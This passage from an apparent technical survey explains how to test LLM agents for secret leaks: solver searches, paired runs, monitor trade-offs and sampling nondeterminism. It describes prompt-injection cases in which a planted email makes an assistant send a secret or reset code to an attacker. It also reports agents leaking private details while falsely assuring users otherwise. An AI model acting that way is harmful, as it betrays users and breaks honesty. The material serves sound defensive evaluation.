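&\wedge\; \alpha(\mathrm{obs}(t)) \neq \alpha(\mathrm{obs}(t')).
\end{aligned}$$

If the solver finds values that make the formula true, those values describe two runs that together show a leak. If it proves that none exist, the model contains no leak within $T$ steps. The search includes shorter runs only if $\mathrm{Step}$ lets a finished run stay in its final state. Otherwise, the tester must repeat the search for each length.

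"No solution" is much stronger evidence than a pair of test runs that agree, because it covers every secret and public input the model can represent. But it doesn't rule out a leak that first appears at step $T+1$. Many tools also limit the number of objects. Macedo and Pacheco's positive result, for example, covers at most three reviewers and three articles, so it would miss a leak that needs a fourth article.

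### AL-Synth

Pandey and colleagues built AL-Synth, a tool of this type for agent workflows that uses a solver and no language model. The user describes a workflow as a set of variables and actions, where each action has a guard (the condition that permits it) and an effect on the variables. For a two-run property, AL-Synth uses the formula above and adds the constraint that the guards must permit every action in each run.

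The tool checks short runs first and increases their length until it finds a violation, so no violation is shorter than the first one it finds. For the scheduling assistant, this first violation is the pair of runs we saw earlier, one with an ordinary meeting and the other with an interview. Both runs take the same three actions: collect, aggregate and report.

AL-Synth can also search for violations that a particular monitor would miss, by adding a condition to the formula that none of the monitor's checks is triggered. Pandey and colleagues did this for nine levels of monitoring and eight types of violation. At the strongest level that uses only one run, the leak through a hidden reason was the only type not covered. The monitor covered the other seven, but with some false alarms for one of them, explicit flows of labelled data.

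AL-Synth was tested on models small enough for a second program to try every possible run. For every type of violation, each violation the solver found was real when replayed, the solver's full list of violations matched the list from the exhaustive search, and its shortest violation had the right length. This is good evidence that the formulas encode the models correctly. It can't show that a model resembles a deployed agent, because the solver and the exhaustive search both start from the same description of the workflow.

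Pandey and colleagues report times for a different problem, in which an agent gradually discloses more than the user agreed to. A single run is enough to show that violation. Finding a shortest violation took about 0.02 to 0.07 seconds for depths up to twelve, while listing all 29,337 violations at depth seven took 118 seconds. They call the result "a shape on one model, not a benchmark", so it doesn't establish how quickly the tool would find leaking pairs in a large workflow. But it suggests that a tester who needs only one counterexample can save most of the time a full search would take.

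### Putting a language model into the formula

In the five-line program, an `if` statement selects slot 10 or slot 11. In a real assistant, the language model determines the selection, and $\mathrm{Step}$ has to describe how. The formula could in principle include the model's arithmetic, but certifying a network that large is computationally infeasible. Nobody has a shorter description that is accurate enough for a proof, and the available substitutes all change what the solver proves.

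One substitute is to let the language model output anything. *Methods for Formal Verification of Agent Skills* (2026) does this for a rule about single sessions, treating the model as an adversary. If the solver shows that the formulas have no solution, then no session up to the bound can break the rule, whichever language model the agent uses. The formulas stay small because they leave out the model's internals, and the solver Z3 handles problems of this size in seconds.

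Unlimited choice is usually too pessimistic for noninterference, because the model may offer slot 10 in one run and slot 11 in the other without having read the calendar. The solver will therefore report a leak whenever the guards allow more than one offer. Such a pair of runs shows that the guards would let a leak through, but not whether any actual language model would behave that way.

A less pessimistic approach replaces the model with an unknown function. The solver assumes only that the same input always gives the same output. For a model that picks words at random, both copies must also use the same random numbers. Suppose the workflow gives the model the list of free slots but not the reasons. Both copies then receive the same input and make the same offer, so the solver can prove that there is no leak, whatever the model is. If the input includes the reasons, some function would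 make different offers, so the solver reports a leak.

Neither substitute can show that an assistant is free of leaks if it reads the reasons but ignores them, because ignoring them depends on the particular model's behaviour, which both substitutes leave out.

The remaining option is to learn a description from observed runs. The survey *Toward Safe LLM Agents* (2026) mentions two systems that do this. ProbGuard represents an agent's runs as a Markov chain, a set of states with fixed probabilities of moving from each to the next. AgentGuard learns a related model while the agent is working and checks properties of that model. A proof about such a model is only as good as the estimated probabilities. The choice of states also matters, because a model whose states don't record whether there is an interview can't show that the interview affects the offer.

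### What a proof about the workflow is worth

A proof about the workflow can still establish which data reaches the language model and which actions the guards permit. Workflow mistakes seem to be common. *Toward Safe LLM Agents* reports that of 18 workflows checked, 27% had structural defects and 55% failed a policy on human approval. The check took less than a second for workflows with up to 5,000 nodes. Comparing two runs is harder because the tool may have to consider every pair of states, which means up to 25 million pairs if each copy has 5,000 states.

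The strongest result of this kind does not use bounded search. The language designed by Garby and colleagues has a machine-checked theorem about its interpreter, the program that runs the agent's code and calls the language model. The guarantee covers runs of any length and does not require a description of how the model chooses. Of the methods discussed here, this is the best option for a developer who can build an agent from scratch and accept the restrictions, but it is less useful for assessing an existing assistant that already reads the whole calendar.

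For that person, a solver is more useful as a source of test cases. Pandey and colleagues reproduced their scheduling pair in a workflow built with LangGraph, a widely used framework for agents. The guard there checked tool permissions, purpose labels, data origin and consent for each action. It allowed all three actions in both runs, although the offers differed, so the gap the solver found also exists in running code. A tester can give the solver's two calendars to a real assistant to see whether its offers differ.

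## How is a paired test of a real agent set up?

A solver can find two calendars on which a model of the scheduling assistant makes different offers. To find out whether the real assistant does the same, a tester has to run it on both calendars and keep everything else the same. In *A Methodology for Information Flow Experiments*, Tschantz, Datta and colleagues (2014) proved that a system violates noninterference exactly when the secret can have a causal effect on what the observer sees, so this test is an ordinary causal experiment. They wanted to know how Google uses information about visitors to choose ads, so they could neither read the program nor control most of its inputs. Someone who tests an agent controls much more, but can still blame the secret for a difference that something else caused.

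### Choosing the secrets

The two secrets must agree on everything the policy releases, so both calendars need the same free slots. The part that differs should be realistic. Searching the output for a planted "canary", such as a random string or an absurd claim, can miss a secret's influence. *Counterfactual Likelihood Tests for Indirect Influence in Private Reasoning Channels* (2026) tried this on a system in which one role writes private text and another continues the work. The second role never repeated a canary, even when it could read the private text. A better probe swapped the private text for another version and measured the likelihood of the same output under the model. The resulting influence score was 54.4% when the second role could read the text and 13.6% when a mask hid it.

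Handwritten pairs can contain unintended patterns. The first version of the customer-data test in *The Oversight Gap* paired each customer's own value with somebody else's. Two language models judged all 40 pairs sound. But the other person's value was larger or later in 25 of the 28 pairs that could be compared this way, so a monitor could beat chance by objecting to large values. The corrected version, described earlier, assigns interchangeable values at random. Three of the original findings did not hold in the corrected version.

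In a test of an agent, such a pattern can mislead the tester about what is leaking, though it does not create a false leak. Suppose the interview always has a longer title than the ordinary meeting, and the assistant's offer depends on the title's length. The assistant does leak, because the title is secret, but the tester may wrongly conclude that it is reacting to the meeting being an interview.

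The secret should also be where the agent would find it in normal use. When Holtzman and West moved the secret word from the system prompt, which holds the developer's instructions, to the user's message, the reader's accuracy on DeepSeek V3.2's stories rose from 77.6% to 93.6%. The secret must not reach the agent by a second route. If the file holding one of the two calendars is named `interview_calendar`, the tester has changed the public input as well.

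### Holding everything else fixed

In *Replayable Financial Agents*, Khatchadourian (2026) lists what a tester should specify before rerunning an agent: the case, the model, the prompt, the tool definitions, the parser that interprets the answer, the stopping rule and the state of the environment. The tester should also record the settings that the program actually sends to the model. One such setting is temperature, which controls how random the model's word choices are. In Khatchadourian's experiments, the logs listed Claude's temperature as zero, but the program had never sent a temperature, so Claude ran at the provider's default.

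Each run should start from the same saved state, with the same simulated time. If the first run starts at 9:55 and the second at 10:05, the assistant may stop offering slot 10 simply because it has passed. If the assistant keeps notes between sessions, the second run can also read what the first one wrote.

Runs can also affect each other while in progress. Tschantz and colleagues compared a browser that collected ads alone with one that ran alongside seven others. In all four repetitions, the browser received a wider range of ads when it ran alone, for example 37 different ads compared with 25. Agents that share a cache, an account or a database could affect each other in the same way.

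Some variation remains even with these controls. According to *Causal Agent Replay* (2026), the output of models hosted by a provider varies even at temperature zero, because of rounding and the way servers group requests. A local model that handles one request at a time with a fixed random seed repeats its output exactly.

### Tools that change things

A test should not send real invitations, and a live tool may return a different result the second time. One solution is to record the first run and reuse parts of it. *Chronicle* (Chawla and Koul, 2026) describes a system that records every point where an agent calls the model, calls a tool or decides what to do next. In a later run, the tester chooses which of these points to execute again and which to replay from the record.

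In a leak test of the scheduling assistant, the calendar tool returns the edited calendar, the model runs live, and a stand-in for the mail tool stores the proposal without sending it. If the model's answers were also replayed from the record, the second run would repeat the first whatever the calendar contained. Chawla and Koul measured the effect of a similar mistake by planting 192 small faults in the safety checks of recorded tools. A test that replayed everything caught none of them because the faulty code never ran. Running the tools live caught 51, including every fault that let the recorded unsafe action through.

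Existing replay tools do not always let a tester give a live agent different tool results, which a leak test requires. One mode of *NovaFabric* (2026) reruns the agent's command but takes both the model's answers and the tools' results from a saved record. An experimental mode lets the tester substitute a different model answer and see how the run continues. Substituting a tool result changes only the saved record, so this mode cannot yet show a live agent a different calendar.

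Recordings fail when the agent asks something new in the second run. Suppose it asked whether a room was free at 10 in the first run and asks about 11 in the second. Chronicle matches calls by tool name and position in the sequence, so it would return the answer about 10. It raises an error only if the number of calls changes. Khatchadourian recommends an explicit rule for handling calls that don't match the recording. If the observer runs the room-booking service, they can already see that the question changed, so the tester may not need an answer to it.

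A simulated tool avoids the problem by computing its answer from the request and a stored state, which the tester resets before each run. Ogundoyin and Ikram (2026) used deterministic tools for this reason in *When Agents Talk, Secrets Travel*, a study of teams of agents. They changed one protected value within each pair and used no live services.

### Comparing runs that take different steps

Agents often reach the same result by different routes. Khatchadourian ran Claude Sonnet 4 three times on each of 50 data-repair cases without changing anything. All three runs gave the same decision in 84% of the cases, used the same set of tools in 56%, and called them in the same order in only 26%. A leak test that flagged any change in the order would have raised a false alarm in 74% of these cases.

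A single extra step can make two similar runs look very different:

```
Run A: read calendar, check room, send proposal
Run B: read calendar, look up colleague, check room, send proposal
```

If the tester compares the runs by step number, every step after the first differs. *AgentDiff* (2026) records where two runs first diverge and how many more steps pass before the second run matches a later step of the first. *Counterfactual Trace Auditing of LLM Agent Skills* (2026) reduces each tool call to a short signature, such as the tool's name and the file it writes, then aligns the sequences of signatures with a standard program. On the runs above, this would find one inserted step. The method in *What Resolve Rate Hides* (2026) also finds blocks of steps that appear in a different order.

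Alignment helps a person see where two runs diverged, but a signature can hide the leak. If the signature contains only the tool's name, proposals for slot 10 and slot 11 look identical. The comparison must keep the contents of whatever the observer receives.

Failures can also look like agreement. When Khatchadourian's program could not find a valid decision in the model's answer, it recorded the last option on the list. Two unreadable answers would therefore count as the same decision. A tester should record failures separately from decisions.

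### Choosing the projection

The projection $\alpha$ should include at most what the observer can see, since a difference they cannot see reveals nothing to them. The observer may be able to see many channels. Ogundoyin and Ikram distinguish seven in a team of agents: the final answer, messages between agents, what the agents send to tools, what the tools return, shared memory, logs, and the files the agents produce.

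Timing can also leak a secret. Dongol (2026), in *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection*, gives an example in which a user approves the exact text of one reply. Before the assistant sends it, an instruction planted in an e-mail makes the assistant try to send a secret to the attacker. A guard blocks this message unless it matches the approved text. The assistant then tries to send the real reply, which the guard allows only if it blocked the first message. The attacker receives the same message either way, but gets it one step earlier when the secret matches the approved text, so a projection that ignores timing misses the leak.

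A narrow projection can also miss leaks in ordinary answers. *Inadvertent Context Leakage in Language Models* (2026) found that models which correctly refuse to state a secret still reveal information about it in harmless-looking outputs. An adversary trained to exploit this recovered full US Social Security numbers from agents built on Claude Opus 4.6 and Gemini 3.1 Pro. A tester who compared only the answers to a direct question about the number would have seen a refusal in both runs and passed the agent.

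Watching every channel creates the opposite problem, because harmless details vary between runs. *The Oversight Gap* works out the trade-off for a monitor that compares one pair of runs and objects if any watched channel differs. Suppose there are $m$ channels. If there is a leak, it is in exactly one of them, channel $j$ with probability $p_j$. Each channel also varies harmlessly with probability $q_j$, independently of the others. Let $S$ be the set of channels the monitor watches, and define

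$$P_S = \sum_{j \in S} p_j, \qquad \beta_S = \prod_{j \in S} (1 - q_j).$$

$P_S$ is the probability that a leak falls in a watched channel, and $\beta_S$ is the probability that no watched channel varies harmlessly. The accuracy then follows in three steps.

1. On a clean pair, the monitor raises a false alarm whenever a watched channel varies, which happens with probability $1 - \beta_S$.
2. On a leaking pair, it always objects if the leak is in a watched channel. Otherwise it objects only if a watched channel happens to vary. The detection rate is therefore $P_S + (1 - P_S)(1 - \beta_S) = 1 - (1 - P_S)\beta_S$.
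3. Averaging the detection rate and the share of clean pairs approved, $\beta_S$, gives the balanced accuracy:

$$\mathrm{BA}(S) = \tfrac{1}{2}\,[\,1 - (1 - P_S)\beta_S + \beta_S\,] = \tfrac{1}{2}\,(1 + P_S\,\beta_S).$$

Adding a channel raises $P_S$ but lowers $\beta_S$ whenever the channel can vary harmlessly. Detection and false alarms therefore rise together. Adding channel $j$ improves accuracy only if $(P_S + p_j)(1 - q_j) > P_S$, which is the same as

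$$\frac{p_j\,(1 - q_j)}{q_j} > P_S.$$

If 100 channels are equally likely to carry the leak and each varies harmlessly 10% of the time, the left side is $0.01 \times 0.9 / 0.1 = 0.09$. Adding a channel therefore improves accuracy until the watched channels cover 9% of possible leaks. Accuracy peaks at nine channels, stays the same at ten and falls after that.

| Channels watched | False alarms | Leaks caught | Balanced accuracy |
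|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | 10.0% | 10.9% | 50.5% |
| 10 | 65.1% | 68.6% | 51.7% |
| 100 | 99.997% | 100% | 50.0% |

The best possible accuracy is about 52%, barely better than guessing. Even the 68.6% in the second row is mostly luck, because only a tenth of leaks are in a watched channel and the monitor catches the rest because something harmless changed at the same time.

Making the channels more stable helps far more than choosing among them. If each varied harmlessly only 1% of the time, the monitor could watch all 100 and reach 68.3%. So it is better to compare the slot offered than the wording of the offer, because the assistant can phrase the same offer in dozens of ways while the slot remains 10.

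The calculation is for a monitor that has a single pair and treats every difference as equally suspicious. A tester with many runs can learn how often each channel varies and give less weight to the unstable ones, so 52% is not a limit on paired testing in general.

*The Oversight Gap* also measured the trade-off, using seven language models as monitors. Each reply stated the value a customer had asked for and mentioned another detail in passing. The models compared only the requested value under the narrow rule and counted any difference under the broad rule.

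| Rule | Leaks caught in the requested value | Leaks caught in the passing detail | False alarms |
|---|---|---|---|
| Narrow | 99.7% | 1.4% | 0.9% |
| Broad | 100% | 90.4% | 75.7% |

Under the broad rule, the formula predicts a false alarm on every clean pair. The measured rate was lower because some models ignored harmless rewording despite their instructions. GPT-4o ignored it most often, which cut its false alarms to 6%, but it then caught only 40% of the leaks in the passing detail.

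A tester can use the narrow rule for the verdict and the broad rule to collect differences for a person to inspect, since neither rule would work alone as an automatic alarm for all leaks. If some of the differences seem to change with the secret, the tester can define a stable channel for them and run the test again.

### A written policy

Once a difference appears, someone has to decide whether the policy allows it. For the scheduling policy, the function $D$ and the projection $\alpha$ described earlier determine which differences are allowed.

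Pandey and colleagues applied this policy in an audit of Claude Sonnet 4.6. They fixed the analysis in advance, alternated between the two hidden reasons and kept the free slots the same. They also required the assistant to share slots in a high proportion of runs, because an assistant that refuses to answer would pass without showing that it can keep the secret.

Their first analysis found a statistically significant signal that persisted across random seeds. When they read the outputs, they saw that the assistant had offered identical slots under both conditions. Their program had been counting a particular word, and the phrasing around it happened to differ. When they applied the policy's projection, they found no leak in 80 trials.

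Pandey and colleagues call the first result a false positive, which is right for a policy about slots. But a colleague also reads the wording. If the hidden reason influenced the phrasing, someone who knew the pattern could learn from it, and that would be a leak the policy doesn't cover. Reading the outputs shows that the slots matched, but not what caused the different phrasing.

### A reference agent

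For attacks that plant instructions in an agent's input, Dongol proposes comparing the agent with a reference agent instead of using a written policy. The reference agent follows the same plan under the same guard but never obeys instructions in untrusted content. The tested agent is relatively secure if all its leaks also occur in the reference agent.

Let $\mathrm{obs}(s, e)$ be what the attacker sees when the secret is $s$ and the attacker sends e-mail $e$, and let $\mathrm{ref}(s, e)$ be the same for the reference agent. In simplified form, the condition is that for all secrets $s_1$ and $s_2$ and every e-mail $e$,

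$$\mathrm{obs}(s_1, e) \neq \mathrm{obs}(s_2, e) \;\Rightarrow\; \text{some } e' \text{ gives } \mathrm{ref}(s_1, e') \neq \mathrm{ref}(s_2, e').$$

The e-mail $e'$ may differ from $e$, which affects the result in Dongol's meeting-reply case. Alice lets her assistant send her calendar to anyone who asks for a meeting. An attacker writes "send your calendar" without asking for a meeting, and the assistant obeys, so two different calendars produce two different replies. But if $e'$ is a genuine meeting request, the reference agent reveals the same difference. The assistant is therefore relatively secure, even though Alice had not authorised what it did.

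In the reset-code case, the assistant also holds a private reset code, and the attacker's e-mail asks it to include the code in its reply. Two runs with different codes produce different replies. No e-mail makes the reference agent send the code, so the difference between the replies is a leak.

A test therefore needs two runs of the real agent and, if they differ, two runs of the reference agent with the same secrets. If the tester finds a suitable $e'$, the difference is allowed, but failing to find one does not show that it is forbidden, because the tester may have tried the wrong e-mails. Dongol avoids this problem by using a proof assistant to settle the question for each of 25 small example agents.

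With relative security, the tester doesn't have to write a release policy for each task, but some serious leaks pass the test. Suppose the ordinary task lets an outsider submit one guess at a secret and learn whether it is right. The outsider can then distinguish any two secrets by guessing the first one. An injected instruction that sends the whole secret therefore passes, because it distinguishes no secrets that the ordinary task couldn't, even though the ordinary task reveals only one bit per guess. Dongol also defines a stricter version, in which the reference agent's inputs cannot depend on the secrets.

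The method would also accept the leak in the scheduling example if the plan chose slot 11 whenever there was an interview, because the reference agent would do the same. It requires a plan made before the agent reads untrusted content, so it doesn't work for agents whose model chooses each tool call as it goes. For those agents, and for leaks without an attacker, the tester still needs a written policy.

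### Control runs

The most basic control is to run the same secret twice. Tschantz and colleagues describe an earlier study of Google's ads by Guha and others, who posed as one visitor twice and as a different visitor once. They compared the ads shown to the two identical visitors to measure how much ads vary when the profile stays the same. With this baseline, the study found that a profile of a gay man received many more ads for nursing schools, a connection few people would notice by reading the ads. If two runs of the scheduling assistant with the ordinary meeting produce different slots, a different slot in the interview run is not evidence of a leak.

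Runs without any secret show what the agent does by default. *AgentTell* (Shahriar, Rahman and colleagues, 2026) used such runs in a large test of agents that operate a web browser. In each task, the agent learned something private on one website, then chose among options on a second. Some options matched possible values of the secret, and a general option completed the task without revealing anything. For example, an agent read that its user belonged to a trade union, then registered the user for an event either through the union or as an individual. The user had told the agent not to share personal details with any website.

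The benchmark has 100 tasks, and six models completed 9,760 sessions. In the 7,630 sessions where the agent held a secret, it chose the matching option 61.1% of the time. Three controls support the conclusion that the secret caused these choices:

- The researchers used every possible value as the secret in turn. Agents chose a given option in 61.1% of sessions when it matched the secret and in 1.2% when the secret was something else.
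- They shuffled the options in each session. An agent that always chose the same position would have matched the secret only 17.9% of the time.
- In the remaining sessions, the agent went straight to the second website without learning the secret. It chose the general option 87.2% of the time, compared with 31.2% when it held a secret.

The researchers measured how often an agent with the secret chose the matching option, then subtracted how often an agent without the secret did. This score averaged 83.0 percentage points for personal attributes, account settings and links to particular documents or assignments, but only 2.6 for which bank the user has. The average was 70.7 when the earlier task required the agent to use the secret and 32.0 when the secret was merely on the page. A test that doesn't require the agent to use the secret may therefore understate the leak.

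In 34.5% of the leaking sessions, the agent's final message assured the user that it had disclosed no personal information. The tester therefore has to read the second website's log instead of relying on the agent's account.

The websites were simple and artificial, with an option for each possible secret, so the 61.1% is not an estimate for ordinary browsing. The benchmark also counts any release as a violation of the privacy instruction. Some tasks ask for resources relevant to the user, who might want the agent to open the page for their profession. But the instruction leaves little doubt about secrets such as union membership.

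A test should also include a case in which a leak is almost certain, to confirm that the comparison can detect one. Holtzman and West did this by giving models the word without asking them to keep it secret. The reader then identified the right story 97% to 100% of the time for four of the five main models. When a language model compares two runs, it also makes sense to show it each pair in both orders, as Holtzman and West did because several models tended to favour one position.

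### Randomising the order

The tester should decide at random which secret each run receives. Otherwise, anything that changes over time, such as the load on a server, can look like an effect of the secret. Random assignment also allows a simple test of whether chance explains the result. Suppose the tester randomly gives five runs the meeting calendar and five the interview calendar, and the assistant offers slot 10 in every meeting run and slot 11 in every interview run. If the calendar had no effect, the same ten offers would have occurred under any assignment. There are 252 ways to split ten runs into two groups of five, and only one puts every offer of slot 11 in the interview group, so the probability of this split by chance is 1 in 252, or about 0.4%. Tschantz and colleagues recommend this method, called a permutation test, because it needs no model of how the system works and remains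 valid even if the runs affect each other.

Without random order, a classifier can sometimes tell the first member of a pair of runs from the second, as Ogundoyin and Ikram's study shows. They took 244 pairs that differed in one protected value, which neither run disclosed, and gave a simple classifier 33 features, such as the number of tool calls. The classifier was right 50.2% of the time after one turn, 56.6% after five and 50.0% after twenty. The result at five turns was far outside what chance would produce.

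But the first member of every pair had also run first, so the classifier may have detected the order of the runs rather than the protected value. One feature, a count of certain tool calls, was higher for the first member in eight pairs and for the second in none. There is no reason to expect this pattern from the protected values, because their order within each pair was arbitrary. Ogundoyin and Ikram therefore attribute the signal to how they built the pairs, and say they would need to randomize the order or repeat the runs to settle the question.

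The same objection weakens their negative results at one and twenty turns. Suppose diagnosis A makes an agent call more tools and diagnosis B makes it call fewer. If A comes first in half the pairs and second in the rest, the effects cancel out, and a classifier looking for a consistent difference between first and second members finds nothing. To detect this kind of leak, the tester has to run each scenario several times with each value and compare the results within that scenario.

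## What does random sampling do to the comparison?

Most agents produce different outputs when a tester runs them twice with the same secret. A rule that reports a leak whenever two runs differ will therefore also flag agents that ignore the secret. *The Oversight Gap* proves that if two runs with the same secret differ with probability $v$, the rule's false-alarm rate is exactly $v$. When the rule compares the full text of a sampling model's answers, $v$ is close to 1.

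### Why flagging every difference fails

The rule raises a false alarm half the time for a harmless scheduling assistant that tosses a fair coin to choose between slots 10 and 11.

A leaking assistant might toss the coin when the hidden reason is an ordinary meeting but always offer slot 11 when it is an interview. One run with each calendar would also give different results half the time, so the rule raises alarms no more often than it does for the harmless assistant, even though the total variation distance is 0.5, which is a large leak.

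The comparison needs a baseline for each secret. Let $P(x)$ and $Q(x)$ be the probabilities of output $x$ under the two secrets. Two independent runs with different secrets differ with probability $1 - \sum_x P(x)Q(x)$. Two runs with the same secret differ with probability $1 - \sum_x P(x)^2$ or $1 - \sum_x Q(x)^2$. If we subtract the average of the two same-secret rates from the different-secret rate, we get

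$$\tfrac{1}{2}\sum_x \big(P(x) - Q(x)\big)^2,$$

which is zero exactly when the distributions are equal. For the leaking assistant, the same-secret rates are 50% with the meeting and 0% with the interview, so the excess is 50 − 25 = 25 percentage points. A tester who repeated only the meeting calendar would have found no excess.

This works for outputs with few possible values, such as the slot. If the assistant almost never words a message the same way twice, all three rates are close to 100% and their difference is too small to measure.

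*The Oversight Gap* also gave this rule to seven language models. The models compared two freely reworded answers from the customer-data task and should have scored 50%, but they averaged 78.9% because six of them again ignored the rewording. Qwen-72B followed the rule literally and scored 55%. When the models compared only the stated value, the average was 88.4%.

### Two definitions for random agents

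Generalised noninterference requires only that the same outputs remain possible when the secret changes. The assistant described earlier satisfies it, even though it offers slot 11 in 90% of runs with an interview and 10% without one. Language models make this definition even weaker than that example suggests.

A language model writes one token at a time, where a token is a word or part of a word. In Hydari and Iqbal (2026), in *The Token Not Taken*, a tutorial on why agents vary, the model gives each possible token $i$ a score $z_i$, and the sampler turns the scores into probabilities:

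$$p_i = \frac{\exp(z_i/T)}{\sum_j \exp(z_j/T)}.$$

Here $T$ is the temperature. Exponentials are always positive, so in exact arithmetic every token is possible at every step, and the assistant could produce any finite text whatever the secret is. An assistant that announced the interview in 99.99% of runs where there was one would satisfy generalised noninterference, because it could also write the same sentence, with tiny probability, when there was no interview.

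Many samplers discard such unlikely tokens, but this can make an assistant fail over a small difference in probabilities. Top-p sampling keeps the smallest set of most likely tokens whose probabilities add up to at least $p$. Suppose $p$ is 0.95 and the model gives slots 10 and 11 probabilities of 94% and 6% with one calendar, and 96% and 4% with the other. The sampler keeps both slots with the first calendar but only slot 10 with the second. The assistant fails because slot 11 is possible with only one of the calendars, even though the distance is just 0.06. The 90% and 10% assistant still passes, with a distance of 0.8.

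Probabilistic noninterference compares the probabilities themselves. *PACE* requires a limit on the distance in the worst case. In simplified notation, let $P_{c,s}$ be the distribution of what the observer sees when the secret is $s$ and the agent's context is $c$. The context is everything except the secret, including the user's request, the results of tools and any text an attacker has inserted. The requirement is

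$$\sup_{c}\; \sup_{s_0,\, s_1}\; d\big(P_{c,s_0},\, P_{c,s_1}\big) \;\le\; \delta,$$

where $d$ is a distance such as total variation, and $\sup$ means that we take the largest value over all contexts and all pairs of secrets. For the scheduling policy, we would consider only pairs of calendars with the same free slots, and apply the projection before measuring the distance.

The worst case matters because an average can hide a serious leak. An assistant that reveals the interview completely in one context out of 100, and reveals nothing in the other 99, has an average distance of 0.01 but a largest distance of 1. PACE also compares the raw bytes of everything that leaves the agent, in order, so a secret still counts as leaked if the agent encodes it, paraphrases it or splits it across several messages.

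Under this definition, one pair of runs no longer proves a violation. *The Oversight Gap* shows that more runs don't prove one either. If every output is possible under both secrets, any finite set of runs could also have come from an agent that ignores the secret. The property is therefore not k-safety for any k. Smaller leaks also take more runs to detect.

### Setting the temperature to zero

Removing the randomness would be much simpler. Lowering the temperature makes the most likely token more likely, and at zero the program always picks it.

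This changes the agent under test, however. The following table shows two assistants whose choice of slot depends on a single token.

| Probability of slot 10 (meeting, interview) | Distance when sampling | Distance at temperature zero |
|---|---|---|
| 90%, 55% | 0.35 | 0 |
| 51%, 49% | 0.02 | 1 |

At temperature zero, the first assistant always offers slot 10, which hides a substantial leak. The second offers slot 10 with the meeting and slot 11 with the interview, which turns a tiny leak into a complete one. The test is reliable only if people also use the agent at temperature zero.

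Even then, a hosted model's outputs can vary. Computers round numbers, so the order of additions can affect the result. For example, $(0.1 + 10^{20}) - 10^{20}$ gives 0, but $0.1 + (10^{20} - 10^{20})$ gives 0.1. Thinking Machines Lab's *Defeating Nondeterminism in LLM Inference* (2025) shows that the variation in language models mostly doesn't come from a graphics processor's cores finishing in an unpredictable order, which is a common explanation. The company repeated the same matrix multiplication 1,000 times on a graphics processor and got exactly the same numbers each time.

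The variation comes from other people's requests. A server groups requests into batches, and the batch size affects how the server splits up its sums. The rounding therefore changes with the number of users. The company asked a large Qwen model to "Tell me about Richard Feynman" 1,000 times at temperature zero and got 80 different answers. All 1,000 were identical for the first 102 tokens, then 992 said Feynman was born in "Queens, New York" and eight said "New York City". With software that always adds in the same order, all 1,000 answers were identical.

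Rounding changes the output only when the two best tokens have nearly equal scores. Nagisettygari and Sindiramutty measured this on a small Qwen model in *How Much Determinism Can Fine-Tuning Buy?* (2026). Batching changed the chosen token at 62 of 32,640 steps, all among the 4.3% of steps where the two scores were closest. When they ran each text twice without batching, nothing changed.

They also found that a repeatability test can pass by accident. Batches of 8 or 16 changed the gap between the two best scores at about 54% of steps when the texts were 384 tokens long, but at none when they were 512 tokens long. A tester could therefore find perfect repeatability with one calendar and lose it with a slightly longer one.

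Pairing runs can also add variation. Servers often save their work on the beginning of a prompt and reuse it when another prompt begins the same way. Paired runs share their instructions, so the server may reuse work from the first run in the second. *Vosti* (Qin, Du and colleagues, 2026) compared fresh and reused computations in vLLM, a popular program for running open-weight models. With vLLM's standard settings, only 3 of 14 pairs of scores matched exactly for each of two models, a Llama and a Gemma. This is another reason to randomise the order of the runs or clear the saved work between them.

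### How far deterministic inference has come

Software that removes this variation improved greatly during 2026. Qin and colleagues define inference as deterministic if requests with the same prompt and the same random number generator state always produce bit-for-bit identical scores at each position in the answer, whatever else the server is doing.

vLLM and SGLang, a similar program, both have modes intended to achieve this. Qin and colleagues tested two configurations of each while varying the batch, the way the server divided up the prompt, and the reuse of earlier work. On Llama-3.1-8B, three of the four configurations matched in every comparison. On Gemma-3-4B, all four had mismatches in every category. A mismatch in the scores need not change the chosen token, but it means that a tester can't assume the mode works for every model.

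Qin and colleagues then built their own engine, Vosti, with machine-checked proofs that scheduling and reuse do not affect the scores. It matched in all 5,488 comparisons across seven models. It was faster than vLLM's deterministic modes but slower than SGLang's and both programs' standard settings.

The slowdown from deterministic inference is also becoming less of an obstacle. In *Detent*, Xin, Feng and colleagues (2026) found that changing only the load altered SGLang's answers to 33 of 1,319 maths problems under standard settings. Their system holds constant only the choices that let the batch affect the result. It took 1.04 to 1.17 times as long per token as the standard settings, compared with 1.67 to 10.3 times for the existing deterministic modes.

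These tools help testers who run an open-weight model themselves. vLLM's documentation page *Batch Invariance* still describes the mode as beta, and every model it lists as tested has open weights. Someone who uses a model through a provider's service can't choose how the server does its arithmetic. Some providers accept a random seed, but Hydari and Iqbal note that they may promise only a best effort to repeat an answer.

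### Using the same random seed

A tester can also keep the temperature unchanged and give both runs the same random numbers. A sampler typically draws a number $u$ between 0 and 1 and uses it to select a token. Suppose the agent offers slot 10 if $u$ is below the probability of slot 10, and slot 11 otherwise. If that probability is 55% in one run and 50% in the other, the offers differ only when $u$ lies between 0.50 and 0.55, which happens for 5% of seeds. With separate random numbers, they would differ half the time.

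Agreement between such runs is informative. Let $X$ and $Y$ be the outputs under the two secrets for the same random seed. For any event $A$, $X$ can be in $A$ while $Y$ is not only if the outputs differ, so

$$P(A) - Q(A) \;\le\; \Pr(X \in A,\, Y \notin A) \;\le\; \Pr(X \neq Y).$$

The total variation distance is at most the share of seeds for which the outputs differ. If the outputs agree for every seed, the distance is zero and the agent satisfies probabilistic noninterference for that pair of secrets in that context.

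The reverse is not true. Suppose the secret is one bit and the agent XORs it with a random bit, outputting 0 if the two bits are equal and 1 if they differ.

| Random bit | Output if the secret is 0 | Output if the secret is 1 |
|---|---|---|
| 0 | 0 | 1 |
| 1 | 1 | 0 |

A scheduling assistant might toss a coin and, on heads, offer slot 10 for a meeting and slot 11 for an interview, but on tails do the opposite. If two runs share the same toss but have different secrets, their outputs always differ. But each slot has a probability of one half under either secret, so someone who sees only the output learns nothing about the secret. Matching outputs under a shared seed are therefore sufficient for noninterference but not necessary.

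However, the observer must not know the random bit. The example code in vLLM's documentation sets the seed to 42. If a developer left a number like that in a deployed agent, an observer who could guess it and reproduce the coin toss could also work out the secret. To keep the secret from that observer, the outputs should agree when the runs use the actual seed, so a difference between them would be a real leak.

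Shared seeds are most useful for short outputs. The sampler uses one random number per token, in a fixed order. If one run contains an extra word, its later tokens use different random numbers from the corresponding tokens in the other run. From then on, the two runs may differ almost as much as they would with separate seeds. The server also needs deterministic arithmetic, because a rounding change can alter which token is chosen when $u$ is close to the boundary.

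### Scoring the same text under both secrets

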